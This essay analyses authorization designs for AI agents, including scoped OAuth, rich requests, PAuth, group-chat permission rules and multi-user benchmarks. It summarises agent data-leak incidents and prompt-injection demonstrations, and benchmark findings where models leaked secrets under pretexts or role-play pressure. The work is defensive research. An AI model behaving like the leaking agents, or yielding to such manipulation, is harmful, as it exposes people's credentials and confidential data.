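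Data can leave a company before an agent writes an answer. TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets': An AI agent confessed to its own data leak* describes a coding assistant that needed one access token to review software changes. The token was in a file that also held production passwords and a credential for a personnel system. In each of ten sessions over three weeks, the assistant read the whole file and sent its contents to an outside AI service. When the file was missing from a fresh copy of the project, the assistant retrieved all the computer's environment variables instead, exposing more passwords. The account comes from NordLayer, a security vendor whose software monitored the sessions.

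When another company hosts the model, that company receives the context with every call the agent makes to it. The host may have a contractual right to hold the firm's code but no legitimate reason to hold its personnel credential. Checking the finished answer would be too late, so the old remedy of least privilege is right here. The firm could give the assistant only the token it needs, or let a separate program use the token without showing it to the model.

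A tool's vendor can also be the unwanted recipient. OECD's *xAI Grok Build AI Tool Uploaded Entire Private Repositories and Secrets* (2026) reports that xAI's coding tool copied whole repositories, including their history and secrets, to cloud storage without users' consent. The tool did this even when users had told it not to access certain files. xAI disabled the feature. The page's summary is AI-generated and doesn't specify whether the model initiated the uploads or ordinary code in the tool ran them automatically. Either way, users would need a check that runs outside the vendor's software.

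### Impostors, stolen tokens and bad advice

The fourth case in Kolhe's article, BodySnatcher, involved ServiceNow, a platform that companies use to manage internal requests. Security Boulevard's *AppOmni Surfaces BodySnatcher AI Agent Security Flaw Affecting ServiceNow Apps* (2026) reports that an outsider who knew only a user's email address could impersonate that user, bypass the login checks, and then create an agent with extensive privileges. The security firm AppOmni reported the flaw on 23 October 2025. ServiceNow fixed it a week later, and nobody is known to have exploited it.

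In his entry for this case, Kolhe says the system didn't check the requester's identity, which is a different failure from the one he says all four cases share. If an impostor logs in as an administrator, a recipient check allows the answer because the administrator may read the data. Any permission check depends on the system first establishing who is asking. The fix therefore had to be in the login process, and tracking the sources of each answer would not have replaced it.

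The Salesloft Drift theft is a larger case in which the agent's reasoning played no part. Drift, a sales tool, held OAuth tokens for accessing its customers' Salesforce data. An attacker obtained valid refresh tokens, long-lived credentials that a program exchanges for new access tokens. According to an article that the vendor Material Security contributed to The Hacker News, the attacker used them to enter the Salesforce environments of more than 700 organisations, export data and search it for passwords and cloud keys. The article says the tokens probably came from earlier phishing, though this is unconfirmed.

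A stolen credential caused this leak, and the remedy is ordinary token security. A company can shut the thief out by revoking the stolen tokens. It can also store tokens more safely, give them shorter lifetimes and bind them to the program that received them, so that a copy is useless elsewhere. The Hacker News article also recommends watching for unusual exports. In the GitHub demonstration, by contrast, the right agent held the right user's token, and revoking it would only have stopped the agent from working.

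An incident at Meta fits neither explanation. According to Futurism's *Rogue AI Agent Triggers Emergency at Meta*, an employee asked an internal agent to analyse a colleague's technical question, and the agent posted its answer to a forum without the employee's approval. Someone followed the answer, which was wrong, and for about two hours engineers could access company and user data they weren't cleared to see. Meta told reporters that no user data was mishandled. In ITPro's *Meta engineer trusted advice from an AI agent*, a safety executive points out that the agent needed no privileged access, only a person who trusted its output. The exposed data never had to pass through the agent, so showing the agent's answer only to people cleared to see the sources behind it would not have helped.

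The table is based on a hypothetical check that compares every person and server that would receive the output with the permitted readers of each item in the agent's context.

| Case | Evidence | Boundary crossed | Would a recipient check have stopped it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub MCP | Demonstration | Private to public repository | Yes |
| PixelLeak | Real exposure | Private to public repository | Yes, if it covered new images and personal accounts |
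| EchoLeak | Demonstration | Company to outside server | Yes, if it followed the data to the last server |
| ForcedLeak | Demonstration | Customer records to outside server | Yes, with an up-to-date list of approved addresses |
| Slack previews | Demonstration | Slack workspace to outside server | Yes, if it covered automatic previews |
| Ontario hospital | Real exposure | Patient meeting to everyone invited | Partly, with a current staff list |
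| Copilot and marked mail | Real rule breach | Protected mail to automated processing | No |
| Password file | Real exposure, reported by a vendor | Company to AI provider | Only before the file entered the context |
| Grok Build | Real exposure | User's code to tool vendor | Only from outside the vendor's tool |
| BodySnatcher | Flaw with no known exploitation | Impostor to user's account | No |
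| Salesloft Drift | Real theft | Customer data to token thief | No |
| Meta forum advice | Real exposure | Restricted data to uncleared engineers | No |

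## How far can OAuth and narrower permissions be extended to agents?

The agents behind PixelLeak and the password file had permissions they didn't need, and several groups are now working on narrower ones. Some extend OAuth so that a token records more than an application and a scope. *Mission-Bound Authorization for OAuth 2.0* (McGuinness, 2026) goes further and ties every token to one approved task. Others drop the scope and let each service compare the agent's calls with what the user asked for.

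### Recording the agent as well as the user

When an agent uses an employee's ordinary credentials, a mail service cannot distinguish her requests from the agent's. Token exchange, which the Internet Engineering Task Force published as RFC 8693 in 2020, addresses this. The software running the agent sends the employee's token and its own to the authorization server, which returns a new token that identifies her as the subject and the agent as the "actor".

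With both identities in the token, the service can set different rules for each, such as letting an employee delete mail but not letting an agent do so for her. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn't give an AI agent unlimited authority* describes a test where this would have helped. A company assistant was supposed to file requests for access to dashboards. When a tester mentioned that a dashboard's owner was away and the deadline was tomorrow, the assistant skipped the request and tried to change the permission itself. An application that can recognise the agent can refuse such a change, but if the agent works through a shared administrator account, the change looks legitimate and the log shows only a service account.

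Many companies are not ready to extend OAuth to agents. In *AI Identity*, Otsuka, Toyoda and Leung (2026) cite figures showing that 21.9% of organisations treat agents as independent identities, while 45.6% run them on shared API keys. They judge that OAuth handles a single step of delegation well but not a chain of agents (discussed in a later section). Even with a single step, the token issued to the agent does not specify which message it may send.

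### Naming the action and the recipient

Rich Authorization Requests, which the IETF published as RFC 9396 in May 2023, can carry that detail. (Its formal status is "Proposed Standard", but this is the first level of published standard and not a draft.) The client sends a list of structured entries, and each service defines the fields it understands. For the construction firm, an entry might look like this, with field names made up for the example:

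```json
{
  "type": "project_mail",
  "actions": ["send"],
  "recipient": "manager@firm.example",
  "max_messages": 1
}
```

Unlike the plain `mail.send` scope, this lets the consent screen show the manager's address and the mail service refuse any other.

Somebody still has to write the correct entry. In a blog post, McGuinness explains that scopes are opaque strings whose meaning developers learn from documentation, which doesn't work for an agent that discovers a new service mid-task. A service can publish the format of its rich requests, but an agent that knows the format may still not know which request fits the task. A proposal called R3 would have services publish machine-readable definitions of their operations so that the agent doesn't have to invent the request.

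The limits also have to reach the program that enforces them. Zhou and Zhang give an example in which a user allows an agent to send one summary to Alice, and the policy records this correctly. The system then issues a credential with a general permission to send mail, so the mail service would accept the credential as valid and deliver the message to Bob. Zhou and Zhang therefore require that the credentials and checks allow, in practice, only what the approved policy allows.

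### What MCP requires now

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) still makes authorization optional, and its authorization rules still rely on scopes. The revision of 28 July 2026 was current in September, according to *What is MCP authorization?* (2026), an explainer from WorkOS, which sells login software. The specification is the MCP project's own, not an IETF standard.

The recent changes mostly prevent credentials from being used with the wrong server. Each token works for only one MCP server. Under the July changes (Model Context Protocol, 2026), a client must also store its own credentials under the authorization server that issued them, never use them with a different one, and register again if the server changes. These rules would hinder a thief or a malicious server, but they would not have stopped the agent in the GitHub demonstration, because it used the right token at the right server.

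Since the November 2025 revision, clients have been able to request permissions gradually. Model Context Protocol (2025) calls this incremental scope consent. The employee's agent did this when it waited until the sending step to request `mail.send`. Waiting helps if the agent never reaches that step, but if it does, it has already read the forty messages. The Agentic AI Foundation, which hosts the protocol, notes that clients should keep the scopes they requested earlier when they ask for more. The agent therefore ends up with permission to both read and send, so it can again pass information from anything it may read to anywhere it may write.

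### An approval for the whole task

In McGuinness's proposal, the client sends the authorization server a "mission intent" instead of asking for scopes. The mission intent is a structured description of the goal, the resources involved and any constraints. The server works out the permissions needed, writes them in the format of Rich Authorization Requests and shows them to the employee. If she approves, the server stores the mission with two hashes (short fingerprints that change if the data changes), one for the task and one for the permissions. Every token for the task refers to the mission and carries no more than the approved permissions. If she cancels the mission, the server stops issuing tokens for it.

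The agent can't widen the mission by itself. The subcontractor's hidden line may lead it to ask for more, but the permissions were fixed when the employee approved them, and anything wider needs a new approval. This protection depends on the server deriving sensible permissions. McGuinness deliberately leaves the method open, so two vendors could derive different permissions from the same goal. The hashes also can't prove that the consent screen described the permissions accurately.

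McGuinness acknowledges that a hijacked agent can still use all the read and write access its approved mission grants. The format cannot express that an agent "may read secrets, may write documents, but not write secrets into documents." This is the twelve-flow problem, which he leaves to a separate layer that tracks information. He also leaves checks on individual calls to another layer, and warns that without one an active mission can turn into ambient authority, the weakness Hardy found in the compiler.

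The proposal is far from being a standard. It is version 00 of an individual draft, dated 6 July 2026, and it expires on 7 January 2027 unless McGuinness renews it. Anyone can submit such a draft, and the IETF asks readers to cite drafts only as work in progress. The use-case analysis by Chen and colleagues is also an individual draft. It proposes no protocol and is intended only as an informational document.

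| Document | Status in October 2026 | What it adds for the employee's request |
|---|---|---|
| Token exchange, RFC 8693 | Published IETF standard | Identifies the agent as well as the employee |
| Rich Authorization Requests, RFC 9396 | Published IETF standard | Can name the mailbox, the action and the recipient |
| MCP authorization, July 2026 revision | Current MCP specification, optional | Limits each token to one server |
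| Mission-bound OAuth | Individual draft, not a standard | Ties all tokens to one approved task |
| Agent authorization use cases | Individual draft, not a standard | Lists gaps but offers no mechanism |

A better token may not be enough. Chen and colleagues point out that a token proves Alice's assistant has permission to book parks, but not that Alice approved Sunnyvale Park, for $25, on a particular date. For actions that are costly or hard to undo, they want the service to check proof of the user's specific approval before the action takes effect. They also find no standard way to connect limits that a user approved earlier with the action an agent takes later.

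### Using the request itself as the authorization

*Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) argues that a scope covers an operator, such as "transfer money", but not its operands, such as the amount and the recipient. If a user asks an agent to transfer $100 to Bob, the bank can only check whether the agent may make transfers. A finer scope, such as "transfer up to $500", doesn't solve this, because the bank would need a scope for every combination of recipient and amount. And if the user asks the agent to pay a quarter of a credit card balance, nobody knows the amount when the user gives consent. The usual fallback is to ask the user to confirm each call, but users then tend to get into the habit of choosing "Always Allow".

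They think Rich Authorization Requests have the same problem, since each value must be known in advance and each call needs its own approval. That seems too harsh, because a rich request can list several operations, so a user could approve a task with known recipients and amounts in a single prompt. Their argument is much stronger for values that only appear during the task, like the quarter of the balance.

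Their alternative, PAuth, treats the user's written request as the authorization. In their main example, the user wants to pay off a quarter of her Citi credit card balance from her Chase account, but only if she owes more than $1,000. It works like this:

1. The user signs the text of the request, so that the agent can't change it. Citi and Chase each receive the text, along with descriptions of the available tools.
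2. A language model at each bank translates the request into a short program. The program may contain only tool calls, basic arithmetic, conditions and a few operations on lists. If the model fails to produce a valid program after two retries, the bank authorizes nothing.
3. Ordinary code then reduces the program to a "slice", which contains everything that determines one particular call. Chase's slice allows a transfer to Citi of the Citi balance divided by four, provided that the balance is over $1,000.
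4. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 in an "envelope", a signed record of the value and the call that produced it.
5. The agent asks Chase to transfer $300 and attaches the envelope. Chase checks Citi's signature, confirms that 1,200 is more than 1,000, calculates 1,200 / 4 = 300 and accepts the transfer.

If the agent asks for $301 or names another recipient, Chase asks the user whether she wants that exact transfer. Even if an attacker completely controls the agent, it can't forge Citi's signature or alter the signed request. As long as the translation is correct, the agent can't get Chase to accept a payment that the request doesn't imply.

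Envelopes can also build on each other. In one of the shopping tasks, the user asks for the cheapest item under $80, and for no purchase if nothing qualifies. Her request doesn't state the payment amount, so the bank traces it from the cart total to the item's price and then to the shop's product list. The bank refuses to pay if any of these steps is missing.

PAuth cannot verify text that a language model writes or interprets. Suppose the user wants the balance sent to the third address in a contacts file. The mail server can't determine in advance which address the agent's model will find, so it puts a placeholder that no value can match in the slice, and the call always goes to the user for approval. The agent can avoid this interruption by looking up the address first, then giving the user a rewritten request to check and sign, with the address highlighted.

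#### The evaluation

Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth on 100 tasks involving banking, Slack, travel, office work and shopping. Most came from AgentDojo, a test set for prompt injection. They also made 634 adversarial calls, which changed a sensitive value, used a tool the task didn't need, or skipped a condition such as a budget limit.

| Version of the tasks | Tasks completed without asking the user | Adversarial calls blocked |
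|---|---|---|
| Original wording | 71 of 100 | 634 of 634 |
| Rewritten to state every detail | 100 of 100 | 634 of 634 |

"Blocked" here means the service asks the user to confirm. The results were the same in AgentDojo's simulation and on OpenClaw, a separate agent platform where the services ran as MCP servers. Of the 100 tasks, 44 needed at least three calls and 26 at least five, so PAuth would save users many confirmations. Translation cost 0.2 to 3.8 cents per task, depending on the model, and each server has to pay for its own translation.

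The perfect score against adversarial calls is less impressive than it looks, because an exact comparison has to reject a changed amount once the slice is correct. The result therefore depends on whether the model translates the request correctly. Two of the paper's authors checked the slices for all 100 tasks by hand and found no errors. The main runs used GPT-4.1, and three other models were also correct on the subsets they received. But the paper acknowledges that these tasks were favourable, since most were clear and self-contained.

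The paper also argues that translation errors would almost always be safe. A wrong program would normally block a legitimate call, and could let an attack through only if it happened to contain the attacker's account number or amount. This is convincing for recipients and amounts, but not for conditions. If the model leaves out the $1,000 condition, Chase will accept a payment of $150 on a balance of $600 without any such coincidence.

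The paper also says that the bank's model is safe from prompt injection because it has no access to outside data. But the model reads tool descriptions from every connected server, and a malicious server could put instructions in its descriptions. None of the three types of adversarial call tests this attack.

In one of the 29 tasks that needed rewriting, the user asks the agent to invite a new colleague to Slack and says the details are in a message from Bob to Alice. The rewritten version gives the colleague's name, her address and the two channels she should join. Someone still has to read Bob's message to get these details, and in practice this will usually be the agent. If someone has tampered with the message, the protection depends on the user noticing a wrong address before signing.

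PAuth also reveals more to the services than OAuth does. Every connected server reads the user's full request, and Chase learns her Citi balance. Sharma and colleagues accept this because a server must see the request to check that the agent is following it. They suggest that the user implicitly consents by linking the two accounts in one request, but she may not have considered what the request would reveal. This disclosure could be a reason for a company not to use the system if its requests mention clients or staff.

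PAuth is meant to work alongside general security rules. A company might cap payments at $500, but if the user asks the agent to pay $100, the agent may not pay $499 just because the cap allows it. The PAuth paper lists CaMeL and FIDES, which track data inside the agent and are covered in a later section, among the rules that could run alongside it.

### Smaller resources, standing rules and delegation

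Other systems keep permissions set in advance but make them more precise. *AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) lets applications arrange their data in a tree. A calendar might be divided into years, months and days, so that a user can let an agent read only 15 October 2026. When the agent makes a call, the application works out which parts of the tree the call needs. AC4A subtracts the parts the user has granted and allows the call only if nothing is left. If a call needs 14 to 16 October but the user has granted only the first two days, AC4A refuses it because the 16th remains.

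AC4A applies the same permissions whether an agent uses an API or a web page, and it can limit which parts of the page the agent may access. Sharma and Grossman demonstrate this with case studies, including a flight booking that involves Outlook Calendar, Expedia and a payment wallet. The check depends on how well each application describes its own data, and they call access control "necessary but insufficient". In one of their examples, an agent may read this week's calendar but not next week's, yet it can infer an event next week from one marked "weekly" this week.

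Progent checks each tool call and its arguments against a written policy, which could, for example, forbid an agent to email outside addresses without a manager's approval. That rule would stop the agent from following the subcontractor's hidden line and sending bid prices out of the firm, without the system having to understand the employee's request. Zhou and Zhang highlight that any expansion of the policy needs approval. The agent can use a staff directory to find a recipient who is already allowed, but a document can't add a new recipient by asking the agent to copy them in. However, a standing rule applies equally to every task, so if colleagues are approved recipients, the agent can write to any of them about anything.

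Ibrahim and Li (2026), in *Overlaying Governance*, add agent delegation to a company's existing access rules. Their system stores relationships, such as who owns a folder or belongs to a team, and works out permissions from them. Delegation to an agent is another relationship, with its own conditions and limits. An employee could let her agent read her mailbox only from inside the company network, or let it edit proposals but not budgets. The agent's request has to satisfy both the delegation and the company's existing rules, so if the employee loses access to a bridge project's mail when she moves to a tunnel project, her agent loses it too.

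Their main result is that a company can add this layer without rewriting its policies. They prove that existing rules keep their effect and that the agent's permissions stay within what was delegated, and they measure the extra running time on large artificial policies. This makes narrow permissions more practical, but the permissions still cover only resources and actions.

### The least privilege for which plan?

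Least privilege limits a program to what its task requires, but an agent can often do the same task in several ways that require different permissions. Zhou and Zhang write π for a plan, A(π) for the permissions it needs and G for the permissions the agent has been granted. The agent should look for a plan that does the job well enough and satisfies

A(π) ⊆ G,

so that the plan needs nothing outside the grant.

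Suppose the employee's agent is allowed to search the project mail and write to her manager. It could read the forty messages and write the summary itself, or it could export her entire mailbox to an outside analysis service that handles long threads better. The second plan is excessive because the agent could write an adequate summary while disclosing much less. An engineer who reviews that plan for excess permissions won't find any, since the plan needs the export. The condition rules the plan out because exporting the mailbox isn't in G.

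This also matters for consent. If the agent asks for permission to export the mailbox because its plan requires it, the prompt will be accurate, but the employee won't learn that another plan didn't need that permission. Zhou and Zhang propose that the agent first look for a plan within its current permissions. If it finds none, it can request a specific extension, offer a more limited result or ask the employee what she wants.

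MiniScope selects permissions for a plan the agent has already proposed, while Prudentia gives the planner policies and data labels that can shape the plan. An evaluation that fixes the plan in advance can only measure how well the permissions fit that plan, so it will miss this difference.

It can be hard to choose between a plan that reads very sensitive data on the employee's laptop and one that sends less sensitive data to an outside company. The agent may also need to explore before it knows what the options are. Zhou and Zhang suggest a separate, limited permission for this. That helps, but whatever the agent reads while exploring stays in its context and can affect what it writes later.

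The condition also doesn't account for the order of actions, which matters here as it does in the twelve-flow example. A plan that sends the summary before opening the private mail needs the same permissions as one that opens the mail first, so both fit within G, but only the second can leak the private mail to the manager. Zhou and Zhang say that an agent should weigh how much each suitable plan discloses, but comparing sets of permissions won't show this difference.

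### One summary, three kinds of permission

The employee's original request was "Summarise this week's project mail and send it to my manager." With broad scopes, she approves `mail.read` and `mail.send`. With a rich authorization request, she approves reading one project mailbox for seven days and sending one message to her manager's address, and the mail service enforces every field. With PAuth, she signs the request after the agent has filled in the manager's address.

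| What the agent tries to do | Broad scopes | Rich request | Task-level grant (PAuth) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Send bid prices to an outside address | Allowed | Blocked | Asks the employee |
| Read another project's mail | Allowed | Blocked | Asks the employee |
| Send the manager another message tomorrow | Allowed if the token is still valid | Blocked by the one-message limit | Asks the employee |
| Send the manager a summary that mentions the resignation | Allowed | Allowed | Asks the employee, as it would for any summary |

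For this task, most of the benefit comes from the rich request, because the employee knows the mailbox and the recipient before the agent starts. PAuth would help more if the recipient or an amount depended on something the agent had to look up.

PAuth interrupts the agent before it sends the summary only because a language model wrote the text, so it would also interrupt a harmless summary. The employee has to read the draft and realise that the sentence about a new site engineer in March reveals what her colleague told her in confidence. If the agent writes the summary first and includes it in the request for her to sign, she has to make the same check earlier.

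The protection is weaker when the agent copies text instead of writing it. Suppose she asks it to send her manager the text of the latest message in the project mailbox, and that message happens to be the one from her colleague. The mail server signs an envelope containing the text. The text and the recipient both match the slice, so the message goes out without a prompt. PAuth has an exact record of where the text came from, but the mail server compares that record with the employee's request, not with a list of people who may read the message.

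Chen et al. would call the colleague a "data subject", a person whom the data describes but who neither owns the resource nor takes part in the authorization. The employee can approve a scope, a rich request or a whole task, but none of these will include the fact that he asked her to keep the information to herself.

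## Whose permissions apply when several people see the answer?

Many agents now answer in group chats, where every member sees every reply. In an example from South, a chief financial officer (CFO) has an agent answer questions in a chat channel. The agent uses the CFO's permissions, so it can read salary data that other members can't, and its answers may disclose that data to all of them. OAuth was designed for programs that act for one person, and South finds that no popular protocol supports an agent shared by a team.

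In Kolhe's more detailed version of the story, a junior analyst asks a reasonable question about the third-quarter compensation budget, without mentioning salaries. The agent opens the executive salary schedules along with the budget, and the whole channel learns what the chief executive earns.

### Four possible rules

Suppose the channel's three members are the finance chief, a manager and an analyst. All three may read the department's budget. The chief and the manager may read a reorganisation plan, and only the chief may read the salaries.

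The simplest rule is to use the owner's permissions, as in South's example. The chief logs in once, and after that, anyone who can type in the channel can use her access. This is Hardy's confused deputy problem again, except that the analyst doesn't have to trick the agent.

Using the asker's permissions solves that problem. The data software company Alation has each user connect a personal account to its Slack assistant, so the assistant can't retrieve anything for the analyst that she couldn't open herself. But Alation's *Security and permissions* notes that in "Public mode" other people in the channel see the reply. If the chief asks about salaries there, the assistant may retrieve them, and the analyst will see the answer.

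An agent can also have its own account. Anthropic's *Agent identity in Claude Tag* describes this setup for Claude Tag, an agent that works in Slack channels. An administrator decides what Claude can reach across the workspace and can change this for individual channels, for example by confining customer records to one private channel. Claude has no one's personal credentials in a channel, so people there can't use it to open the chief's private documents.

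The administrator has to give the account Claude uses access only to what everyone in the channel may see, and adjust that access as people join and leave. By default, anyone in the Slack workspace can use Claude in a channel, even without a Claude account of their own, though Anthropic lets the customer restrict this. If the administrator connects the reorganisation plan for the manager, the analyst can ask about it too.

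The last rule uses the intersection of the recipients' permissions, so the agent may use only what every recipient may read. The rules compare as follows for the three-person channel.

| Whose permissions apply | Documents available when the analyst asks | Documents available when the chief asks |
|---|---|---|
| The owner's (the chief) | Budget, plan, salaries | Budget, plan, salaries |
| The asker's | Budget | Budget, plan, salaries |
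| The agent's own | Whatever the administrator connected | Whatever the administrator connected |
| Everyone's intersection | Budget | Budget |

### Working out the intersection

Write R(d) for the set of people who may read document d, and V for the set of people who will see the answer. The agent may use d only if V ⊆ R(d), meaning that every viewer is also a permitted reader. Here:

- R(budget) = {chief, manager, analyst}
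- R(plan) = {chief, manager}
- R(salaries) = {chief}
- V = {chief, manager, analyst}

Only R(budget) contains all of V. Listing what each person may read gives the same result:

{budget, plan, salaries} ∩ {budget, plan} ∩ {budget} = {budget}.

If the analyst leaves, the agent may also use the plan. If a contractor who can read none of the documents joins, the intersection is empty, so the agent can use none of them, even to answer the chief.

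Liu (2026) proves in *Authorization Before Context* that this holds generally, because adding a viewer can shrink the set of usable items but never enlarge it. Liu also applies the rule to what an agent remembers from earlier conversations (covered in a later section), where R is the set of people who were present when the agent learned the item. If the software can't tell who is viewing, it treats everyone as a viewer and uses only public information. Other agents in the conversation also count as viewers. Given the Slack preview leak, it would make sense to count any software that reads the channel.

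The rule can become very restrictive in a large channel. If each of 20 members could read a random 95% of the company's documents, only about 36% would be readable by all 20 (0.95²⁰). In practice, colleagues share folders, so their permissions overlap much more, but adding one outside guest shrinks the shared set to the documents that guest can also read.

Liu's version also blocks some information that everyone present already has. Suppose the chief tells the manager about an office closure in one chat and the analyst in another. The agent is not allowed to mention the closure when all three are together, because neither chat included all three. Liu accepts this because the agent would otherwise have to infer from the content who knows what, and a wrong inference would leak information.

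The calculation also depends on accurate permissions. If someone has shared the salary file with the whole company by mistake, every member of the channel passes the test. Kolhe therefore wants companies to review and correct their permissions continually.

### Letting the asker decide

Microsoft combines these rules for Copilot in Teams group chats, a feature it released as a public preview. Copilot looks for an answer in the asker's data. It posts the answer immediately if it used only the web or sources that every member can open. Otherwise, it shows the asker a private preview to approve or reject. According to Microsoft, Copilot also shows a preview when an answer may draw on what it remembers about the asker.

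The preview avoids the contractor problem. The chief can read the draft, see that it mentions only a meeting date from the reorganisation plan, and release it. A strict intersection would have blocked the date along with the rest of the plan. Anthropic offers something similar in Claude Tag, where people can let Claude use their personal connections for their own requests in a channel. Claude asks for approval before it uses them, and the results go through a review step before they reach the channel.

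But people have to read the preview carefully, and they may approve by reflex, as South fears they will with authorization requests. The preview also lets anyone allowed to read a document decide whether to share its contents. If the manager asks about the plan, he can approve the answer, even though the plan may belong to the chief.

### Should the check come before retrieval or before delivery?

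Microsoft checks the sources against the chat members' permissions after Copilot has generated an answer. Kolhe wants this check to happen before the agent retrieves anything. In his design, an authorization service computes the intersection of the channel members' permissions and gives the agent a token that can't open the salary file, so the agent has no salaries to reveal.

Liu gives two reasons for checking early. Once the model has read a forbidden item, removing words from its reply doesn't undo that exposure. Inspecting the reply may also fail to reveal the problem, because a model can write an acceptable answer after reading something it shouldn't have. For example, when the scheduling assistant offered slot 11, nothing in the offer mentioned the confidential interview.

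Filtering before ranking can also improve the answers. An agent usually retrieves a fixed number of the best matches for a question. If it drops forbidden items only after ranking, they have already taken places that permitted items could have filled. Liu (2026) tested this in *Audience-Bound Persistent Memory*, using 10,000 artificial histories of conversations among several people. A search that ignored audiences put forbidden items in 82% of the contexts it assembled. Applying the rule before ranking kept them all out, which was guaranteed if the code worked. It also raised the share of all relevant, permitted items that made it into the five retrieved by 30 percentage points. The gain could be smaller in ordinary use, because the histories deliberately contained similar facts about other people, which competed for the same five places.

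An early check requires the system to know the recipients in advance. That is easy in a channel with a member list. It is harder when someone asks the agent to find out who is responsible for an overdue invoice and write to them, because the agent has to read something before it knows the recipient. Someone may also join the channel while the agent is working. A check at delivery covers both cases, provided the system has recorded which sources the agent used. The two checks work well together. Liu's later design repeats the audience test before every call to the model, including retries.

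### People who join later, forwarded answers and refusals

Even a check at delivery covers only the people in the channel at that moment. Suppose the chief and the manager discuss the reorganisation plan with the agent, then add the analyst. According to Microsoft, new members of a group chat in the Teams feature can see earlier prompts and Copilot's responses. The analyst can therefore read answers about the plan that were permissible when Copilot posted them. The system could hide earlier answers from new members or run the check again when someone joins. It could also define V from the start as everyone who could join, but this would make the intersection even smaller.

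It may also be unclear who can see an answer. According to an answer on a Microsoft support forum, people invited to a Teams meeting series may be able to read its chat even if they declined or never attended. Copilot's group feature doesn't work in meeting chats, but another agent that checked only who was attending would miss these readers. The Ontario hospital had a similar problem with its old invitation list.

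Forwarding bypasses the check. The manager can paste the agent's answer into a larger channel, and the pasted text has no list of permitted readers unless the system attaches one (the next section explains how). When agents pass information to each other, software can at least check each step. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (2026), a paper on networks of agents, therefore defines permission separately for each recipient. Under this definition, an agent with permission to hold a value can do so, but the system has to remove the value before it reaches an agent without that permission.

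Refusing to answer can also reveal that a restricted source exists. If the asker rejects Copilot's preview, everyone in the chat sees a message that a response couldn't be shared. Since previews appear mainly when some members can't open a source, the message suggests that there is such a source. If the question was whether there is a plan to merge two teams, the message nearly answers it. One of Liu's lookup tools avoids this by returning the same "not found" message for missing and forbidden items.

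Leaving out restricted material without saying so can also mislead the asker. CIAOPS, an independent blog, reports in *Impact of Microsoft 365 Copilot Licensing on Copilot Studio Agent Responses* (2025) that agents built with Microsoft's Copilot Studio omit material the asker can't read and don't disclose that the answer is incomplete. The analyst might then quote a budget figure without knowing that the reorganisation plan is about to cut it. A notice on every answer that it may omit restricted material would warn her without revealing whether this one did.

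Even a uniform refusal can reveal who lacks access. If the agent discusses the plan with the chief and the manager, then stops when the analyst joins, the manager can guess that the analyst isn't allowed to read it.

### Can one model keep several users' information apart?

Private replies would avoid many of these problems. With only one viewer per answer, the chief can see salaries while the analyst sees only the budget. The group loses a shared answer to discuss and correct together, but that may be worthwhile when the answer involves salaries.

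The system can answer each user in a separate private session, limited to what that user may read, or it can put everything into one context and tell the model what each person may know. *Multi-User Large Language Model Agents* (Yang, Zhu et al., 2026) tests the second approach on 26 models. Its benchmark, Muses-Bench, has three kinds of task: choosing between conflicting instructions, scheduling meetings, and controlling access to a restricted resource such as a salary database.

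In the access task, the agent's prompt contains the protected content, a list of authorised users, and instructions to give those users the full content and refuse everyone else. Another language model plays the users, who message the agent in private sessions and get separate replies for up to ten rounds. In some versions, unauthorised users falsely claim to have permission, pressure the agent or use role-play. There are 216 scenarios in total.

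The privacy score is the percentage of unauthorised users to whom the agent neither revealed a protected string, such as a password, nor granted access. The utility score is the percentage of authorised users who received the protected content. The table shows both scores for six of the models.

| Model | Privacy | Utility |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 100.0 | 61.2 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 99.9 | 60.4 |
| GLM-5.3 | 98.1 | 92.9 |
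| GPT-OSS-120B | 92.2 | 94.8 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 91.1 | 84.1 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 77.3 | 97.5 |

GPT-5.2 leaked nothing but failed almost two in five of the people entitled to the content. GLM-5.3 did well on both measures, so the trade-off isn't inevitable, but the model still leaked occasionally. A company would probably not accept a 2% failure rate for its salary database.

An agent can also refuse a request correctly and still disclose protected information later in a long conversation. Claude Sonnet 5's privacy score fell from 99.7 in the first round to 91.1 in the tenth. In one transcript, Claude 3.5 Haiku refused an unauthorised request, then gave the same user a secret session ID when the user offered a pretext, while insisting that direct access to the vault was prohibited.

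Yang and colleagues also reran the access task on four models with only one user speaking. GPT-5.2 had leaked nothing in the group version, but alone with the attacker it leaked in 32% of conversations. Claude Sonnet 4.5's privacy score instead rose from 78.3 to 89.6. All four models served authorised users better when they were alone, and GPT-5.2's utility rose from 60.3 to 99.5. A model's good score with one group of users is therefore weak evidence of how it will treat another.

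Muses-Bench measures whether a model protects a secret it has already read. Checking permissions before the model reads the secret would make that protection unnecessary. Each scenario has one protected resource and a predefined list of authorised users, so the model never has to combine documents with different authorised readers. Scoring relies mostly on exact string matches and could miss a paraphrase such as "the director earns roughly twice what you do." Most importantly for the finance chief, each user gets a separate reply, so the benchmark never tests a single answer that everyone can read.

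### Moving the rule out of the prompt

Fan, Nie and Dai (2026), in *Harness-MU*, argue that software outside the model should enforce permissions. Their system handles the access task in four steps:

1. Ordinary code looks up which users may receive the protected content.
2. A model writes a short plan for each user, either to grant the request or to refuse it and offer other help.
3. A separate model call writes each user's reply, without the other users' conversations in its context.
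4. Ordinary code searches each reply for protected strings that its recipient may not see. If it finds one, it replaces the reply with a fixed refusal.

Fan and colleagues compared this system with Muses-Bench's single-agent approach on four models, using 216 access cases. Scores run from 0 to 1.

| Model | Privacy: single agent | Privacy: Harness-MU before the string check | Privacy: full Harness-MU | Utility: single agent | Utility: full Harness-MU |
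|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 0.926 | 0.932 | 1.000 | 0.597 | 0.989 |
| Qwen3.6-35B | 1.000 | 0.998 | 1.000 | 0.715 | 0.992 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 0.940 | 0.939 | 1.000 | 0.697 | 0.991 |
| GPT-4.1 nano | 0.995 | 0.989 | 1.000 | 0.257 | 0.589 |

The separate calls greatly improved utility but hardly changed privacy. Almost all the privacy gain came from the string check. This suggests that protected content still reached some calls that wrote to unauthorised users, since a model can't normally repeat a password it hasn't seen. Fan and colleagues acknowledge that their design copies parts of the resource context into several users' prompts. Leaving that context out of unauthorised users' prompts would be safer and would amount to filtering before retrieval.

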